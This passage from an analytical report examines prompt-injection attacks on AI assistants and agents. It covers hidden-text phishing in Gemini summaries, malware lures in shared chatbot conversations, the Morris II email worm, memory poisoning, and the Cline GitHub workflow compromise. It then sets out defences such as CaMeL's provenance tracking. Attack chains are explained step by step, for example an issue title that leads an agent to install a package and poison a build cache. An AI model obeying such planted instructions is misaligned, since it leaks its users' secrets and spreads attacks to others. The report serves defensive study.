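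## Outputs that deceive readers or carry instructions to other AI systems

A program can check a package name against a list of approved names, but it cannot check prose this way because nobody can list every safe sentence. Output encoding does not help either, because people and language models respond to the meaning of the text. An instruction to call a scammer's phone number does the same harm after encoding.

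Harmful text does not need suspicious wording. The test emails in *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (2026) claim, for example, that a manager has already approved a request or that company policy allows it, and they never give the assistant a direct command. The word "assistant" appears in both the attacks and their harmless counterparts, so a filter cannot use it to tell them apart. The important difference is whether the manager really approved the request, which cannot be determined from the email alone.

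### A false security warning in Gemini's summary

Google's Gemini can summarise a user's emails. *Phishing For Gemini* (Figueroa, 2025) describes a way to make it deliver an attacker's message. A researcher had reported the method to 0DIN, Mozilla's bug bounty programme for AI systems.

The attacker sends an ordinary-looking email that also contains an instruction in white text with a font size of zero, so the recipient sees only blank space. When the recipient clicks "Summarize this email", Gemini receives the email's underlying code, including the hidden text. It follows the instruction and ends the summary with a warning that the recipient's Gmail password has been compromised, along with the attacker's phone number to call.

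A false warning in a Gemini summary appears in Google's own product, in response to the user's request. Paubox's *Flaw in Google Gemini allows email summaries to be used for phishing* notes that many users see these summaries as an extension of Google Workspace, so they may take the warning for a genuine alert. Many people have learned to distrust the same warning when it comes in an email from a stranger. The attacker's email also needs no link or attachment, so a spam filter has little to detect.

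Google replied that it was strengthening its defences and had seen no evidence of real attacks, according to TechBriefly's *How hackers can weaponize Gemini's summary feature* (2025). Google could search delivered emails for hidden instructions, so its statement is some evidence that there had been no real attacks. But researchers had reported similar attacks in 2024, and this one still worked after Google had published countermeasures. 0DIN rated the social impact as moderate, because an attacker can email huge numbers of people but each victim has to ask for a summary and then act on it.

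### Malware instructions in shared AI conversations

Criminals have used AI answers to deceive people in a simpler way, without hiding anything from the model's user. Huntress' *AMOS Stealer Exploits AI Trust* describes an infection the security company investigated on 5 December 2025. The victim searched Google for a way to clear disk space on a Mac. Two of the top results led to conversations on the genuine websites of ChatGPT and Grok, another chatbot. The victim opened the ChatGPT conversation and pasted a command from it into Terminal, the Mac program that runs typed commands. The command installed Atomic macOS Stealer (AMOS), which steals passwords and cryptocurrency.

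Chat services let users publish their conversations as web pages. Engadget's *Hackers tricked ChatGPT, Grok and Google into helping them install malware* describes how attackers ask an assistant about a common search term, prompt it to recommend a command that installs malware, and publish the conversation. Readers see a real answer on the assistant's official site, but an attacker prompted the assistant to give it.

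Engadget reports that the attackers paid Google to promote the pages to the top of the search results, while Huntress says they manipulated the search rankings. If the attackers bought advertisements, Google could have stopped them by checking where the advertisements led.

macOS has a safeguard called Gatekeeper that checks downloaded applications, but it does not inspect commands that a user pastes into Terminal, so the victim saw no warning. The malware asked for the "System Password", checked it in the background and used it to take full control of the computer. It also looked for two cryptocurrency wallet applications and replaced them with fakes that asked for the owner's recovery phrase. Huntress discovered the lure only by working backwards from an alert about the malware, after data had begun to leave the machine.

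Huntress found similar results for several related searches, and Kroll's *New AMOS infection vector highlights risks around AI adoption* describes another case where instructions hosted on ChatGPT led to the same malware. In February 2026, Trend Micro reported that attackers had uploaded hundreds of malicious agent skills to two public collections to spread a version of AMOS. In this case, the attackers first manipulated the agent, then used a fake dialogue box to ask its user for a password.

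The financial losses are unknown. Huntress describes one victim in detail but does not estimate how many others there were. Microsoft has observed Mac malware campaigns using several kinds of deception since late 2025, but its observations do not show how many people fell for AI conversations in particular.

### Morris II: an email that copies itself

A deceptive output can also copy itself when its reader is another AI system. In *Here Comes The AI Worm*, Cohen, Bitton and Nassi (2024) built Morris II, an attack that copies an instruction from one email assistant to the next. It is named after the Morris worm, which spread across the internet in 1988. A worm is malicious software that copies itself from one computer to another.

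The assistants in the experiment searched a mailbox for relevant emails and gave them to a model, which wrote a new email. The attacker's email contained an instruction to include private information from the other emails in the answer and to repeat the instruction itself. If *G* is the model and *w* is the instruction, the attack works when

*G*(ordinary text + *w*) = new text + *w* + private information.

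The output contains *w*, so it can infect the next assistant that reads it. Cohen and colleagues list four conditions for this kind of spread:

- The assistant accepts messages from other people.
- It automatically adds new messages to the collection that it searches.
- It exchanges messages with other users' copies of the application.
- It uses material from its collection to write those messages.

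Morris II sent the private information to whoever the user was writing to, not to the attacker, because the model wrote the email but the application chose the recipient. Some of the information was also false. When the model had to list the addresses in ten emails, 26% of the addresses it gave did not appear in them. With 100 emails, this rose to 37%. The model had often invented an address from a person's name.

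### How quickly Morris II could spread

Cohen and colleagues tested the worm on real emails from Enron, an American energy company whose staff emails became public. They built a mailbox of 100 emails for each of 20 employees and added the worm, which began with a paragraph about Enron. Gemini 1.5 Flash then wrote 3,000 emails. When it received 20 emails as context, it included both the instruction and private information in about a fifth of its replies and expanded drafts. Cohen and colleagues conclude that the worm would reach a new assistant about once every five emails.

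This rate depends heavily on the mailboxes being small. An assistant that picks 20 emails at random from about 100 will include the worm about 20% of the time, close to the rate in the experiment. In a separate test, the assistant retrieved 70% of the mailbox, so the worm would be included 70% of the time by chance. It was included 77.1% of the time with the Enron paragraph, the best opening, but only 19.5% of the time when it began with a general greeting.

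The following table shows what random retrieval would mean for larger mailboxes, if the model always copied the worm after retrieving it.

| Emails in the mailbox | Chance of retrieving the worm among 20 emails | Emails written per new infection |
|---|---|---|
| 100 | 20% | 5 |
| 1,000 | 2% | 50 |
| 10,000 | 0.2% | 500 |

An attacker who knows what the victim writes about could do much better. Infected replies also add copies of the worm to the mailbox, which raises the chance that the assistant retrieves one.

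Cohen and colleagues tested the copying itself by always giving the model the worm and passing it through chains of 20 employees. The instruction and the theft of information worked more than 90% of the time up to the eleventh step, but only 40% to 80% of the time by the twentieth. Results differed between models, with Claude 3.5 Sonnet staying at around 100% and Gemini 1.5 Pro falling to 64%.

*Here Comes the AI Worm* (Cohen, 2025), the version for a security conference, gives a faster-sounding figure of 20 new infections per infected assistant within one to three days. At the earlier rate of one infection per five emails, infecting 20 others would take 100 emails to different people, or 33 to 100 a day. Some sales or support staff send that many, but most people do not.

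A worm keeps growing only if each infected assistant infects more than one other, on average, before someone removes the worm from it. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) uses an example of two groups of agents, with invented infection rates, to show why an organisation has to calculate this average for all its agents together.

| Source of the infection | New infections among networked agents | New infections among isolated agents |
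|---|---|---|
| One networked agent | 0.75 | 0.40 |
| One isolated agent | 0.55 | 0.45 |

The worm would die out within either group alone, because the within-group infection rates, 0.75 and 0.45, are both below one. But the groups also infect each other. With both within-group rates below one, the worm still grows if the product of the two cross-infection rates exceeds the product of the amounts by which the within-group rates fall short of one. Here, 0.40 × 0.55 = 0.22, which exceeds 0.25 × 0.55 = 0.1375, so the number of infections rises by about 9% each round. Blocking messages between the groups would stop the growth even if no individual agent became harder to deceive.

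### Detecting the copied instruction

Cohen and colleagues also built a detector, the Virtual Donkey, which works because the worm must copy itself to spread. The detector compares the model's output with each email in its input, using three standard measures of overlapping text. A small classifier then uses the highest scores to predict whether the output contains a copied instruction. If so, the application warns the user before sending the email. The detector takes little compute because it does not use another model to read the text.

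The researchers trained and tested the detector on 10,000 outputs, half of them infected. It caught every worm in the test and wrongly flagged 1.5% of harmless emails. The perfect detection rate was partly due to the threshold, which the researchers had set to catch every worm. But the detector also caught them all at its default threshold, with 2.8% false alarms. One of the three measures, METEOR, did slightly better alone than all three together, with 1.2% false alarms.

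The detector also worked well on worms with other goals, and slightly less well on worms that made the model obey in other ways. It was less reliable on a collection of Hillary Clinton's emails, where it scored a randomly chosen infected output higher than a randomly chosen harmless one 79% to 97% of the time, depending on the measures used. An organisation would therefore have to test the detector on its own mail before relying on it.

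Cohen and colleagues did not test attackers who try to evade the detector. An attacker could tell the model to translate or reword the instruction each time, which would reduce the overlap. The detector may also flag harmless replies, because many email programs include the previous message in a reply. Skipping the quoted text would avoid these false alarms, but a worm there could go undetected.

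### Later experiments and the evidence from real systems

*Responsible Development of Offensive AI* (2025) repeated the Morris II attack on Falcon3, an open model released in December 2024, and found that it still worked. Other researchers have extended the idea beyond email. *Prompt Injection 2.0* (2025) summarises work by Lee and Tiwari on malicious instructions that pass between agents within a single system. *The Promptware Kill Chain* (2026) describes AgentHopper, which spreads between coding assistants through shared code repositories. *Autonomous LLM Agent Worms* (2026) uses a controlled environment to study how worms spread between different agent platforms.

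The most realistic demonstration is in En Klype Salt's *Context Collapse, Part 3* (2026), where Håkon Måløy describes worm-like spread through a commercial product, Copilot in Microsoft Word. Måløy gave Microsoft the prompts and instructions for reproducing the attack, and twice extended the original 90-day deadline, eventually to 144 days. Antipov (2026), in *Скрытые команды в Word заставляют Copilot распространять ИИ-червя*, reports that the attack still worked after two patches and two versions of the underlying GPT model.

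In September 2026, OpenAI announced that GPT-Red, its automated attacker, had found self-copying injections that worked on the company's own models. CBINEWS's *AI版蠕虫攻击现身* (2026) describes the simplest one. A user asked an agent to answer an email from a personal trainer's assistant. Hidden text in the email asked for a reply in Spanish that quoted the whole message, supposedly so that a scheduling system could index it. The agent complied, and its reply carried the hidden text to the recipient. The request looks much more like normal office correspondence than the Morris II instruction did, and the copying looks like ordinary quotation.

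Other attacks did more damage. Cross (2026) reports in *OpenAI's GPT-Red Finds Self-Replicating Prompt Injections* that a false system warning made an agent delete a folder of reports before copying the attack into a file. Another injection made an agent remove a security check from a software build script. All of this happened in simulations, and in each published example a single agent copies the attack and no second agent passes it on.

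OpenAI had seen no sign of these attacks in real incidents. The following month, a report by Anthropic identified AI worms as a new threat, according to *AI Worms* (Mousicos, 2026). The experiments show that models can copy instructions and that commercial assistants can spread them. *Compositional Threat Analysis* warns that evidence for every step of an attack shows only that the complete attack is feasible, not that one has occurred.

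### False entries in an agent's memory

An injected instruction normally disappears when the conversation ends. But if the agent saves it to long-term memory, it can affect later conversations, even after the attacker's original message is gone. An attacker can plant such an entry with a forged web request, like the one described earlier that stored a false payment address. An agent can also create one itself by summarising a malicious email and saving the summary.

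Suppose an assistant reads an attacker's email claiming that a supplier has changed banks, and saves the new account number as a fact about the supplier. Three weeks later, an employee asks the assistant to prepare a payment, and it retrieves the saved number and fills in the attacker's account. The email did not ask for a payment, and the employee's request was genuine, so neither conversation looks suspicious by itself, and an investigator who examines only the payment conversation will not find the attack.

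Some entries take effect only when the agent retrieves them for a related question. These are harder to notice because they may go unused for months. Others load at the start of every session and can affect every task.

Replacing the model does not remove either kind. *Compositional Threat Analysis* recommends isolating a poisoned memory and rebuilding it from records that show where each entry came from. Without such records, the owner may have to delete the whole memory. An application can reduce this risk by recording each entry's source and asking for approval before saving anything from outside material. For payments, it should take the account number from the company's supplier records, which the agent cannot change.

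### Defences for human readers

The most direct defence against the Gemini attack is to remove hidden text before the model reads the email. Figueroa suggests looking for text that is white, transparent or of zero size. Rules for particular styles can miss others, such as pale grey text on a white background, so a better filter would pass the model only the text the user can see. Figueroa also suggests telling the model to ignore hidden text, but this has the same weakness as the written allow-list in TicketOracle.

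A second filter can check the summary for phone numbers, links and urgent security language. Blocking all of these would make many summaries less useful, since a delivery message may properly include the courier's number. The filter could instead remove only contact details that don't appear in the email's visible text, which would catch the attacker's number because it was in the hidden code. The false warning might remain, but the reader would have no number to call. An attacker could get around this by also putting the number in a visible signature.

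Showing sources would also help. If the summary marked the warning as text from the email, the reader would know that it did not come from Google. Shared conversations need a similar label, because the official web address hides that a stranger wrote the prompts. A prominent notice beside any command in a shared conversation would only slightly inconvenience honest users. The attacks that Figueroa and Huntress describe are good reasons for such measures, but neither source measured how many people would still be deceived. Some readers will ignore any label, especially when a warning seems urgent.

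### Defences against spread between assistants

Marking outside content for the model is less dependable than marking it for a person, because an assistant still has to use the contents of an email to answer it. OpenAI now includes self-copying attacks in training and expects future models to resist them better. This should help against attacks similar to known ones, but Måløy's result in Word shows that new model versions do not necessarily stop a particular attack.

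Cohen and colleagues suggest saving only emails from known senders, or only those that the user has answered. This would stop many first infections from strangers. The filter is less useful once a worm has started to spread, because the next copy comes from one of the user's own colleagues. It also leaves the assistant with less material for its answers.

Requiring a person to approve each email slows a worm, and Morris II would have been easy to spot because it added extra sections to every message. Attackers can make the instruction invisible, but the private information would still appear in the draft. Approval is also less reliable when the leak looks like part of a normal answer. *Enterprise AI Must Enforce Participant-Aware Access Control* (2025) warns that a malicious sender can extract information from a mailbox even if its owner reviews every draft. The assistant can avoid this by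 using only material that the recipient is allowed to see.

Limits in the application's code do not depend on anyone noticing the attack. OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* compares an agent to a customer support worker. Employers expect some customers to deceive these workers, so they limit what the workers can do. An email assistant could have a daily limit on automatic messages and need approval to write to several people at once. If a worm infects one assistant for every five emails sent, and each infected assistant can send only four automatic emails before someone removes the worm, each infection leads to fewer than one new infection on average. Researchers have not tested such limits on a live email system, and the right number would depend on how quickly the organisation finds and removes infected messages.

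## The Cline incident: from an issue title to an unauthorised software release

An agent that can run commands in a shell is much harder to contain than an assistant that only writes email. In February 2026, someone published an unauthorised version of Cline, an open-source AI coding tool. Cline's developers had given a model access to a shell in the system that builds their software, and had let strangers write part of the model's prompt.

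### Automated builds and release credentials

Software teams usually automate building, testing and releasing their programs. On GitHub, they write the steps in a file called a workflow. An event, such as a new bug report or a set time of night, starts the workflow, and GitHub runs the steps on a temporary virtual machine called a runner. The runner receives any passwords and keys that the workflow specifies.

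A release workflow needs a publishing token, a secret string that lets anyone who has it upload new versions of a package to a registry such as npm. Someone who steals the token can therefore release software under the project's name.

To save time, workflows store downloaded files in a cache and reuse them in later runs. Adnan Khan (2026), the security researcher who discovered the flaw in Cline's project, explains in *Clinejection* that all workflows on a project's main branch can read and write the same cache, even if they don't use caching themselves.

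### An issue sorter that could run commands

Cline's users report bugs by opening issues on GitHub, which anyone with an account can do. On 21 December 2025, the developers added a workflow that gave each new issue to Claude Opus 4.5 to analyse and answer.

The workflow used Claude Code Action, Anthropic's component for running Claude on GitHub. By default, the component responds only to people who have permission to change the project's code. Cline's developers opened it to everyone, gave the model a shell and put each issue's title directly into the prompt. Cline's *Post-mortem* describes this as equivalent to giving every GitHub user shell access.

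The developers did restrict the workflow in other ways. It could read the project's code but not change it, and the only secrets it directly exposed were its restricted GitHub token and a key for using Claude. The publishing tokens were in a separate workflow that released a test version every night.

### From the issue title to a publishing token

Khan worked out how an attacker could get from one workflow to the other by opening a single issue:

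1. The attacker writes an issue title that looks like an error message and tells the model to install a helper package before continuing.
2. The model runs the install command, and a script in the package starts the attacker's program on the runner.
3. The program fills the shared cache with more than 10 GB of junk, which makes GitHub delete the existing entries. It then saves altered files under the names that the nightly release workflow looks for.
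4. The nightly workflow loads these files, and the attacker's code runs on a machine that has the publishing tokens.
5. The code sends the tokens to the attacker.

Khan tried the first two steps on a copy of the project, and Claude ran the install command in every attempt. The command looked fairly harmless because its address seemed to belong to Cline's own project. Snyk's *How “Clinejection” Turned an AI Bot into a Supply Chain Attack* (2026) explains that GitHub also makes code from other people's copies of a project available under the original project's address. An allow-list that accepted every address under Cline's name would therefore have let the package through.

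The third step had recently become easier. A workflow can't overwrite an existing cache entry, and GitHub used to clear an overfull cache only once a day. From 20 November 2025 it did so immediately, so an attacker could remove the genuine entries and replace them within minutes.

GitHub discards the runner after each job, but the cache remains. A sandbox is not enough when trusted programs outside it later use files the agent wrote.

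The nightly tokens were also more powerful than they needed to be. npm ties a token to a package, and Cline used the same package for its nightly and full releases. The two marketplaces for its editor extension, VS Code Marketplace and OpenVSX, tie a token to a publisher, and Cline used the same publisher for both kinds of release. Cline required a maintainer to approve each full release, but a thief with a nightly token could publish one without approval.

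### Unanswered reports and a public test

Khan reported the flaw on 1 January 2026, through GitHub's private reporting system and by email. He wrote again on 8 January, messaged Cline's chief executive on 18 January and tried a final time on 7 February. On 9 February he published his findings, and Cline removed the vulnerable workflows within 30 minutes. The flaw had existed for 50 days, including 39 after Khan first reported it.

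Someone tried the attack on 28 January, 12 days before Khan's article appeared, so that attempt was not copied from the article. Bargury (2026) found it in an archive of public GitHub activity and describes it in *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent*. The issue's title contained an instruction for the model to install a package, much as in Khan's tests. The account that opened the issue had a name imitating that of GitHub's automation. Its owner closed the issue about five minutes later and changed the title to "user error".

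Bargury concludes that the attacker probably found the method in Khan's test copy of the project, where Khan's test issues had been publicly visible since 2 January. Testing in a private copy would have kept them hidden. But Cline had received Khan's report almost four weeks before the attack and could have prevented it by removing the workflow.

### What is confirmed and what is inferred

| Claim | Status | Evidence |
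|---|---|---|
| Any GitHub user could get the model to run commands | Confirmed | The workflow file, Khan's tests and Cline's account |
| Someone attempted the attack on 28 January | Well supported | Archived GitHub records |
| An attacker altered the cache | Likely | Unusual failures in the nightly workflow |
| The attacker stole the npm token through the cache | Inferred | The timing, and a known route that fits |
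| Someone used a stolen npm token on 17 February | Confirmed | Cline's account |
| The same person was behind the attempt and the release | Inferred | Bargury's reading of the records |

Nobody has published a log showing the token leaving Cline's systems. The package in the January attempt was designed to download a further script, which its owner deleted and Bargury could not recover. Khan considers the issue workflow the most obvious route but says the attacker's way in is unclear. Cline explains how an attacker could have used the workflow but does not state that this attacker did. The Hacker News (2026) reports that the attack Khan described is "exactly what happened", but offers no further evidence of the theft.

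Bargury believes the attacker was a bug bounty hunter, someone who looks for flaws in return for rewards. The same account had probed a test project where the software company New Relic invited such attempts, and the unauthorised release did little harm. Bargury's explanation is plausible, but a criminal might also start with a harmless trial.

### Warning signs before the release

Between 31 January and 3 February, several nightly releases failed at a final clean-up step, which printed nothing instead of its usual few lines. Khan had been checking Cline's public build records for signs of an attack since he discovered the flaw. He recognised the pattern because Cacheract, a tool he had published to demonstrate cache attacks, replaces that step and causes this kind of failure when the replacement doesn't work properly.

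The builds failed visibly only because the attacker's code fitted badly. A better-made attack could have left them looking normal, so a team can't rely on failed builds to reveal an attack. Checking the cache would have been a better way to detect this one, since an issue sorter has no reason to write more than 10 GB to it.

A much clearer warning came on 10 February, when Khan received an anonymous email from someone who claimed to have working npm and OpenVSX tokens for Cline. Khan forwarded the email to the company. The npm token did work, but the OpenVSX token probably did not, because Cline says it had replaced that token the day before.

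### The token that Cline missed

Cline had begun replacing its credentials on 9 February. It replaced the tokens for the two extension marketplaces, but deleted the wrong npm token and left the exposed one active. The team then checked npm's token management page for the organisation, which showed no active tokens. The exposed token may have belonged to an individual account, which would explain why the page did not list it. *Supply Chain Attack targeting Cline installs OpenClaw* (Plate, 2026) traces the token to an account called clinebotorg.

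On 11 February, Cline told Khan that it had revoked all the publishing tokens. It also said that it had checked every release up to 9 February and found no unauthorised ones, so users did not need to do anything. The check was accurate, but it could not show whether a thief still had a working token, and on 17 February someone used one.

The reliable way to check that a credential has been revoked is to try it. The team can send npm a harmless request with the old token, such as one asking which account it belongs to, and npm should reject the request. GitHub does not display stored secrets, so a team that overwrites the old token first may have no copy left to test. It can avoid this by running the test from a workflow before replacing the token. The team can also compare the token's fingerprint, a short code computed from it, with the registry's record to help it delete the right token.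 Cline now requires checks like these and no longer relies on a dashboard.

Cline could also have blocked the unauthorised release by setting npm to accept only trusted publishing, in which the build system proves its identity and receives a short-lived credential. According to Plate, Cline had set up trusted publishing but still allowed ordinary tokens. The token Cline had missed when it deleted the wrong one therefore still worked.

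### Eight hours on npm

At 11:26 UTC on 17 February, someone used the token to publish version 2.3.0 of Cline's command-line program. The attacker's only changes were a new version number and an install script that also installed OpenClaw, a legitimate AI agent. OSV's *GHSA-9ppg-jx86-fqw7* (2026) records that Cline published a clean version at 19:23 and marked the unauthorised one as deprecated at 19:30, about eight hours after its release.

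The security company StepSecurity flagged the release at 11:40, just 14 minutes after it appeared, Likhith (2026) reports in *Cline Supply Chain Attack Detected*. StepSecurity's monitor compares new releases with earlier ones, and three differences stood out:

- An ordinary npm account had uploaded the package, whereas earlier releases came from GitHub Actions, GitHub's build service.
- The package had no provenance record, a signed statement of which source code and build it came from.
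- It contained a new install script.

The detection time is StepSecurity's own figure, and the company sells the monitor. But Plate's account, based on the package and npm's public records, confirms the three differences.

The alert came at 3:40 a.m. Pacific time, and the release stayed available for almost eight more hours. A one-day waiting period before installing new packages would have blocked the release even without an alert.

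Likhith puts the number of downloads at about 4,000. This is consistent with the package's normal traffic, since Plate counts 418,545 downloads in the 30 days to 17 February, or about 4,650 in an average eight hours. But build systems and scanners also download packages automatically, so the number of affected computers is unknown. Microsoft's threat researchers, quoted in The Hacker News, saw a "small but noticeable uptick" in OpenClaw installations that day.

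The official advisory rates the severity as low. Likhith is more worried, because OpenClaw can run commands and normally leaves a service running in the background. However, Plate found that the release did not install or start this service, so the low rating seems fair for the release itself. Bargury's objection that the rating understates the breach is also fair, because the token would have let the thief publish any program under Cline's name. The extension tokens were potentially more dangerous, because Cline's extension has more than five million installs and many copies update automatically. If the thief had stolen those tokens too, nothing would have prevented them from publishing a malicious update to the extension before 9 February.

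### Auditing the other releases

After the unauthorised release, Cline audited everything it had published since 21 December. It compared the npm packages file by file with the source code. It also matched every published version of the extension to a marked version of the code and to an authorised workflow run. It found no other unauthorised releases.

The npm check is more convincing than the audit of the extension. In the attack Khan described, the attacker's code runs inside an authorised nightly build, so it could alter the extension before publication and the result would still match a genuine run. Only a comparison of the contents would reveal the change, and Cline describes such a comparison only for npm. There is, however, no sign that anyone tampered with the extension.

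Provenance records have the same limitation, because they show which build produced a package but not whether an attacker interfered with that build. Cline now publishes to npm only through trusted publishing, which removes the long-lived token but would not stop malicious code inside the release workflow. Cline has also decided to stop using the cache in release workflows, which addresses that problem directly.

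Cline also removed the AI issue sorter and said that any future version would have read-only access and no shell. It is also setting deadlines for answering security reports, which might have prevented the incident.

### How common the configuration is

On 4 December 2025, 17 days before Cline adopted this configuration, the security company Aikido published a warning about it in Daelman's *PromptPwnd*, which describes workflows that put strangers' text into a prompt and give the model powerful tools or secrets. Daelman called the setting that Cline later used, which opens Claude Code Action to everyone, "extremely dangerous".

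Aikido found the pattern at at least five Fortune 500 companies and in Google's project for Gemini CLI, a coding agent. Google's workflow gave the model only a few commands, for printing text and for viewing, editing and commenting on issues. In Aikido's tests on a private copy, these were enough for the model to follow a planted instruction to write secret keys into the text of the issue. On a public project, anyone could have read them there. Google fixed the flaw within four days.

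The largest survey so far is *Demystifying and Detecting Agentic Workflow Injection Vulnerabilities in GitHub Actions* (Wang, Hou and colleagues, 2026). The researchers built a program that traces outsiders' text through workflows, and ran it on 13,392 workflows that use AI. It flagged 519 workflows. After reviewing these by hand, the researchers judged 496 of them, across 440 projects, to be exploitable, or 3.7% of the total. In 86.5% of the exploitable cases, the attacker could use the title or body of an issue, as in Cline's project.

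In most cases, a later script used the model's answer without checking it, for example to label an issue, so the model did not need shell access. The consequences therefore range from a wrong label to stolen secrets, and the count does not show how many workflows could lead to an incident as serious as Cline's.

The rate varied enormously between the components that developers used to run a model. The shares below come from dividing the researchers' counts.

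| Component | Can restrict who starts it | Workflows | Exploitable | Share |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code Action | Yes | 5,212 | 13 | 0.2% |
| Codex Action (OpenAI) | Yes | 492 | 14 | 2.8% |
| Claude Code Base Action | No | 227 | 20 | 8.8% |
| Gemini CLI Action | No | 244 | 31 | 12.7% |
| AI Inference (GitHub) | No | 795 | 393 | 49.4% |

Claude Code Action and Codex Action don't run for strangers unless the developer changes a setting, and few developers seem to change it in a dangerous way. Cline's configuration was therefore unusual among users of Claude Code Action. The comparison with AI Inference is imperfect because that component is often used to summarise or label issues from the public, so more of its workflows have to read strangers' text. Still, secure defaults probably explain part of the difference. Only 21 of the 1,033 AI components that Wang and colleagues examined offered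 any control over who could start them.

Microsoft (2026) reports attempts to inject instructions into these workflows in public projects that use agents from several companies. In one attempt, a request for a diagnostic feature contained instructions for an agent to add an invisible image to a documentation page. If a maintainer had accepted the change, a script in the image could have stolen the session tokens of people who visited the page. The attempt took place in a copy of a well-known project, and Microsoft suspects that the attacker was testing which attacks would work.

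### Limiting agents in build systems

Microsoft's June 2026 guidance recommends a "Rule of Two", which says that a workflow should have at most two of three things: untrusted text as input, access to secrets, and the ability to change things and communicate with the outside. Cline's issue sorter had all three. It read issue titles written by strangers, held a key for Claude, and had a shell with network access. Teams applying the rule also need to count indirect access. The sorter had no publishing tokens, but it could write to a cache that a workflow with those tokens would later read.

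Restricting an agent's tools works only if the developer knows what each tool can reach. Microsoft found that Claude Code Action could run shell commands in a sandbox that hid the runner's secrets, but its file-reading tool worked outside the sandbox. In Microsoft's test, a planted request for a "compliance review" made the model read its own API key and leave out the first few characters, so GitHub's secret scanner did not recognise it. Anthropic fixed the flaw on 5 May 2026, six days after Microsoft reported it.

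Wang and colleagues suggest keeping the issue's title and body out of the prompt. The workflow would pass only the issue number, and the agent would fetch the text with a restricted command. This separates the developer's instructions from the stranger's text, but the model still reads both. Daelman found that secrets usually leaked even when Claude fetched the text itself, so the change is not enough for an agent with powerful tools.

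Newer models resist many of these attacks. *GitInject* (Isbarov, Suleymanov and colleagues, 2026) ran each attack five times in real GitHub workflows. Four attacks hidden in issues or proposed code changes failed every time against Claude Sonnet 4.5, Haiku 4.5 and Opus 4.7. But five failures in five runs are compatible with a success rate as high as 43%. Khan's fake error message also worked every time on Opus 4.5, a model of the same generation.

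Isbarov and colleagues had more success with instruction files. Coding agents read a file in the project, such as CLAUDE.md, for the owner's standing instructions. An outsider can include one in a proposed change, and the workflow may load it before the agent reviews that change. In one test, the researchers used the file to tell the agent not to comment on how security code compares values, and the agent missed a flaw planted there. It found the flaw when the file was absent. Such attacks worked on seven of nine models, but not on Claude Opus 4.7 or GPT-5.4.

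The researchers also measured how much protection each defence gave and how much useful work it prevented.

| Defence | Attacks that still worked, out of 9 | Normal tasks that still worked, out of 5 |
|---|---|---|
| None | 9 | 5 |
| Not saving the project's access token on the runner | 6 | 5 |
| Restricting the agent's tools | 5 | 4 |
| Removing instruction files and similar documents | 3 | 4 |
| All three | 2 | 4 |
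| All three, and no automatic review for unknown contributors | 0 | 3 |

The first defence needs only a one-line change and has no measured drawback, so there is little reason not to use it. Two attacks still worked against all three defences. One got the agent to approve bad code, and the other ran up the owner's bill for the model. Excluding unknown contributors stopped both, but many open-source projects introduced automatic review specifically to handle contributions from unknown people.

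None of the nine attacks used the cache, so the table does not show which defence would have protected Cline. Khan's more specific recommendations for this case are to remove the sorter's shell and its ability to write files, keep the cache out of release workflows, and publish nightly versions under a separate package name with their own token.

An issue sorter can work without giving the model any tools. The model reads the issue and returns one label, and ordinary code checks the label against a fixed list before applying it. An attacker who controls the model's answer can then only get an issue mislabelled. But the project's developers would have to write the replies themselves, which was the work Cline had hoped to save.

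## CaMeL: checking where data came from before acting on it

An issue sorter without tools is safe because it can do very little. But many assistants must both read strangers' text and send emails, share files or make payments. CaMeL, short for "capabilities for machine learning", is a design for such assistants. Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues at Google DeepMind and elsewhere presented it in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). CaMeL assumes that an attacker can control the output of any model that reads outside text, and it limits what that output can do rather than relying on the model to recognise attacks.

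### Separating planning from reading

CaMeL builds on the design in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023). In that design, a privileged model receives the user's request and can call tools, but never sees emails or web pages. A quarantined model reads that material but has no tools. When the quarantined model summarises an email, ordinary software stores the summary under a name. The privileged model can use that name to have the software display the summary, without seeing the text itself.

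Instructions in an email can then no longer control the model that has the tools. But Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, describes a flaw that the DeepMind team found. Suppose a user asks the assistant to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in some meeting notes. The quarantined model has to read the notes to find the address. An attacker who can write in the notes can make it return a different address. The privileged model then takes the steps the user wanted, but sends the document to the wrong address.

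CaMeL therefore has four parts:

- A planning model turns the user's request into a program in a restricted version of Python.
- A reading model extracts values from untrusted text and cannot call tools.
- An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and records each value's sources and permitted readers.
- A policy for each tool, also written in code, checks these records before the tool runs.

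The split can also improve privacy. Reading is the easier task, so a small model on the user's own device may be good enough for it. The company that provides the planning model would then not receive the user's emails.

### One request, step by step

Suppose a user writes, "Send offer.pdf to the address in Bob's last email." The planning model sees only this sentence and a description of the tools. It writes a program like this:

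```
email = get_last_email(sender="Bob")
address = ask_reading_model("Find the address", email, EmailAddress)
file = get_file("offer.pdf")
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=file)
```

The interpreter runs the program and keeps these records:

| Value | Source | Permitted readers | Trusted? |
|---|---|---|---|
| "Bob" and "offer.pdf" | The user's request | Anyone | Yes |
| `email` | Bob's message | The user and Bob | No |
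| `address` | Bob's message, through the reading model | The user and Bob | No |
| `file` | The user's own files | The user and Ana, a colleague | Yes |

The policies always allow the assistant to fetch an email or a file, but the policy for `send_email` requires the recipient's address to come from a trusted source and the recipient to be one of the file's permitted readers. Neither is true here, so the interpreter pauses and prompts the user to approve or refuse sending offer.pdf to this address. If the user's policies already listed the address as trusted and allowed it to receive the file, the interpreter would send the email without prompting the user.

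Suppose Bob's message contains a planted instruction to forward the whole mailbox to an attacker. The reading model may follow it, but it can only return an email address. The program has no step that forwards a mailbox, and nothing in the message can add one. At worst, the reading model returns the attacker's address, the user approves it, and the attacker receives one file.

The interpreter shows the user the same question whether the address is genuine or the attacker's, because both would come from the same email. Provenance shows that a value is untrusted but not whether it is wrong. The question therefore needs to include the full address and its source, so that the user has some basis for deciding.

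### The rule in formal terms

Let *S*(*x*) be the set of sources of a value *x*, and *R*(*x*) the set of people who may read it. When a program computes *z* from *x* and *y*, the new value gets

*S*(*z*) = *S*(*x*) ∪ *S*(*y*) and *R*(*z*) = *R*(*x*) ∩ *R*(*y*).

A value computed from two others keeps all the sources of both, but only people allowed to read both may read it. If Ana, Bob and Carla may read one document, and Bob, Carla and Dev another, only Bob and Carla may read a summary of both. Tracking data in this way is called information-flow control. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a related design from Microsoft that uses the same rule.

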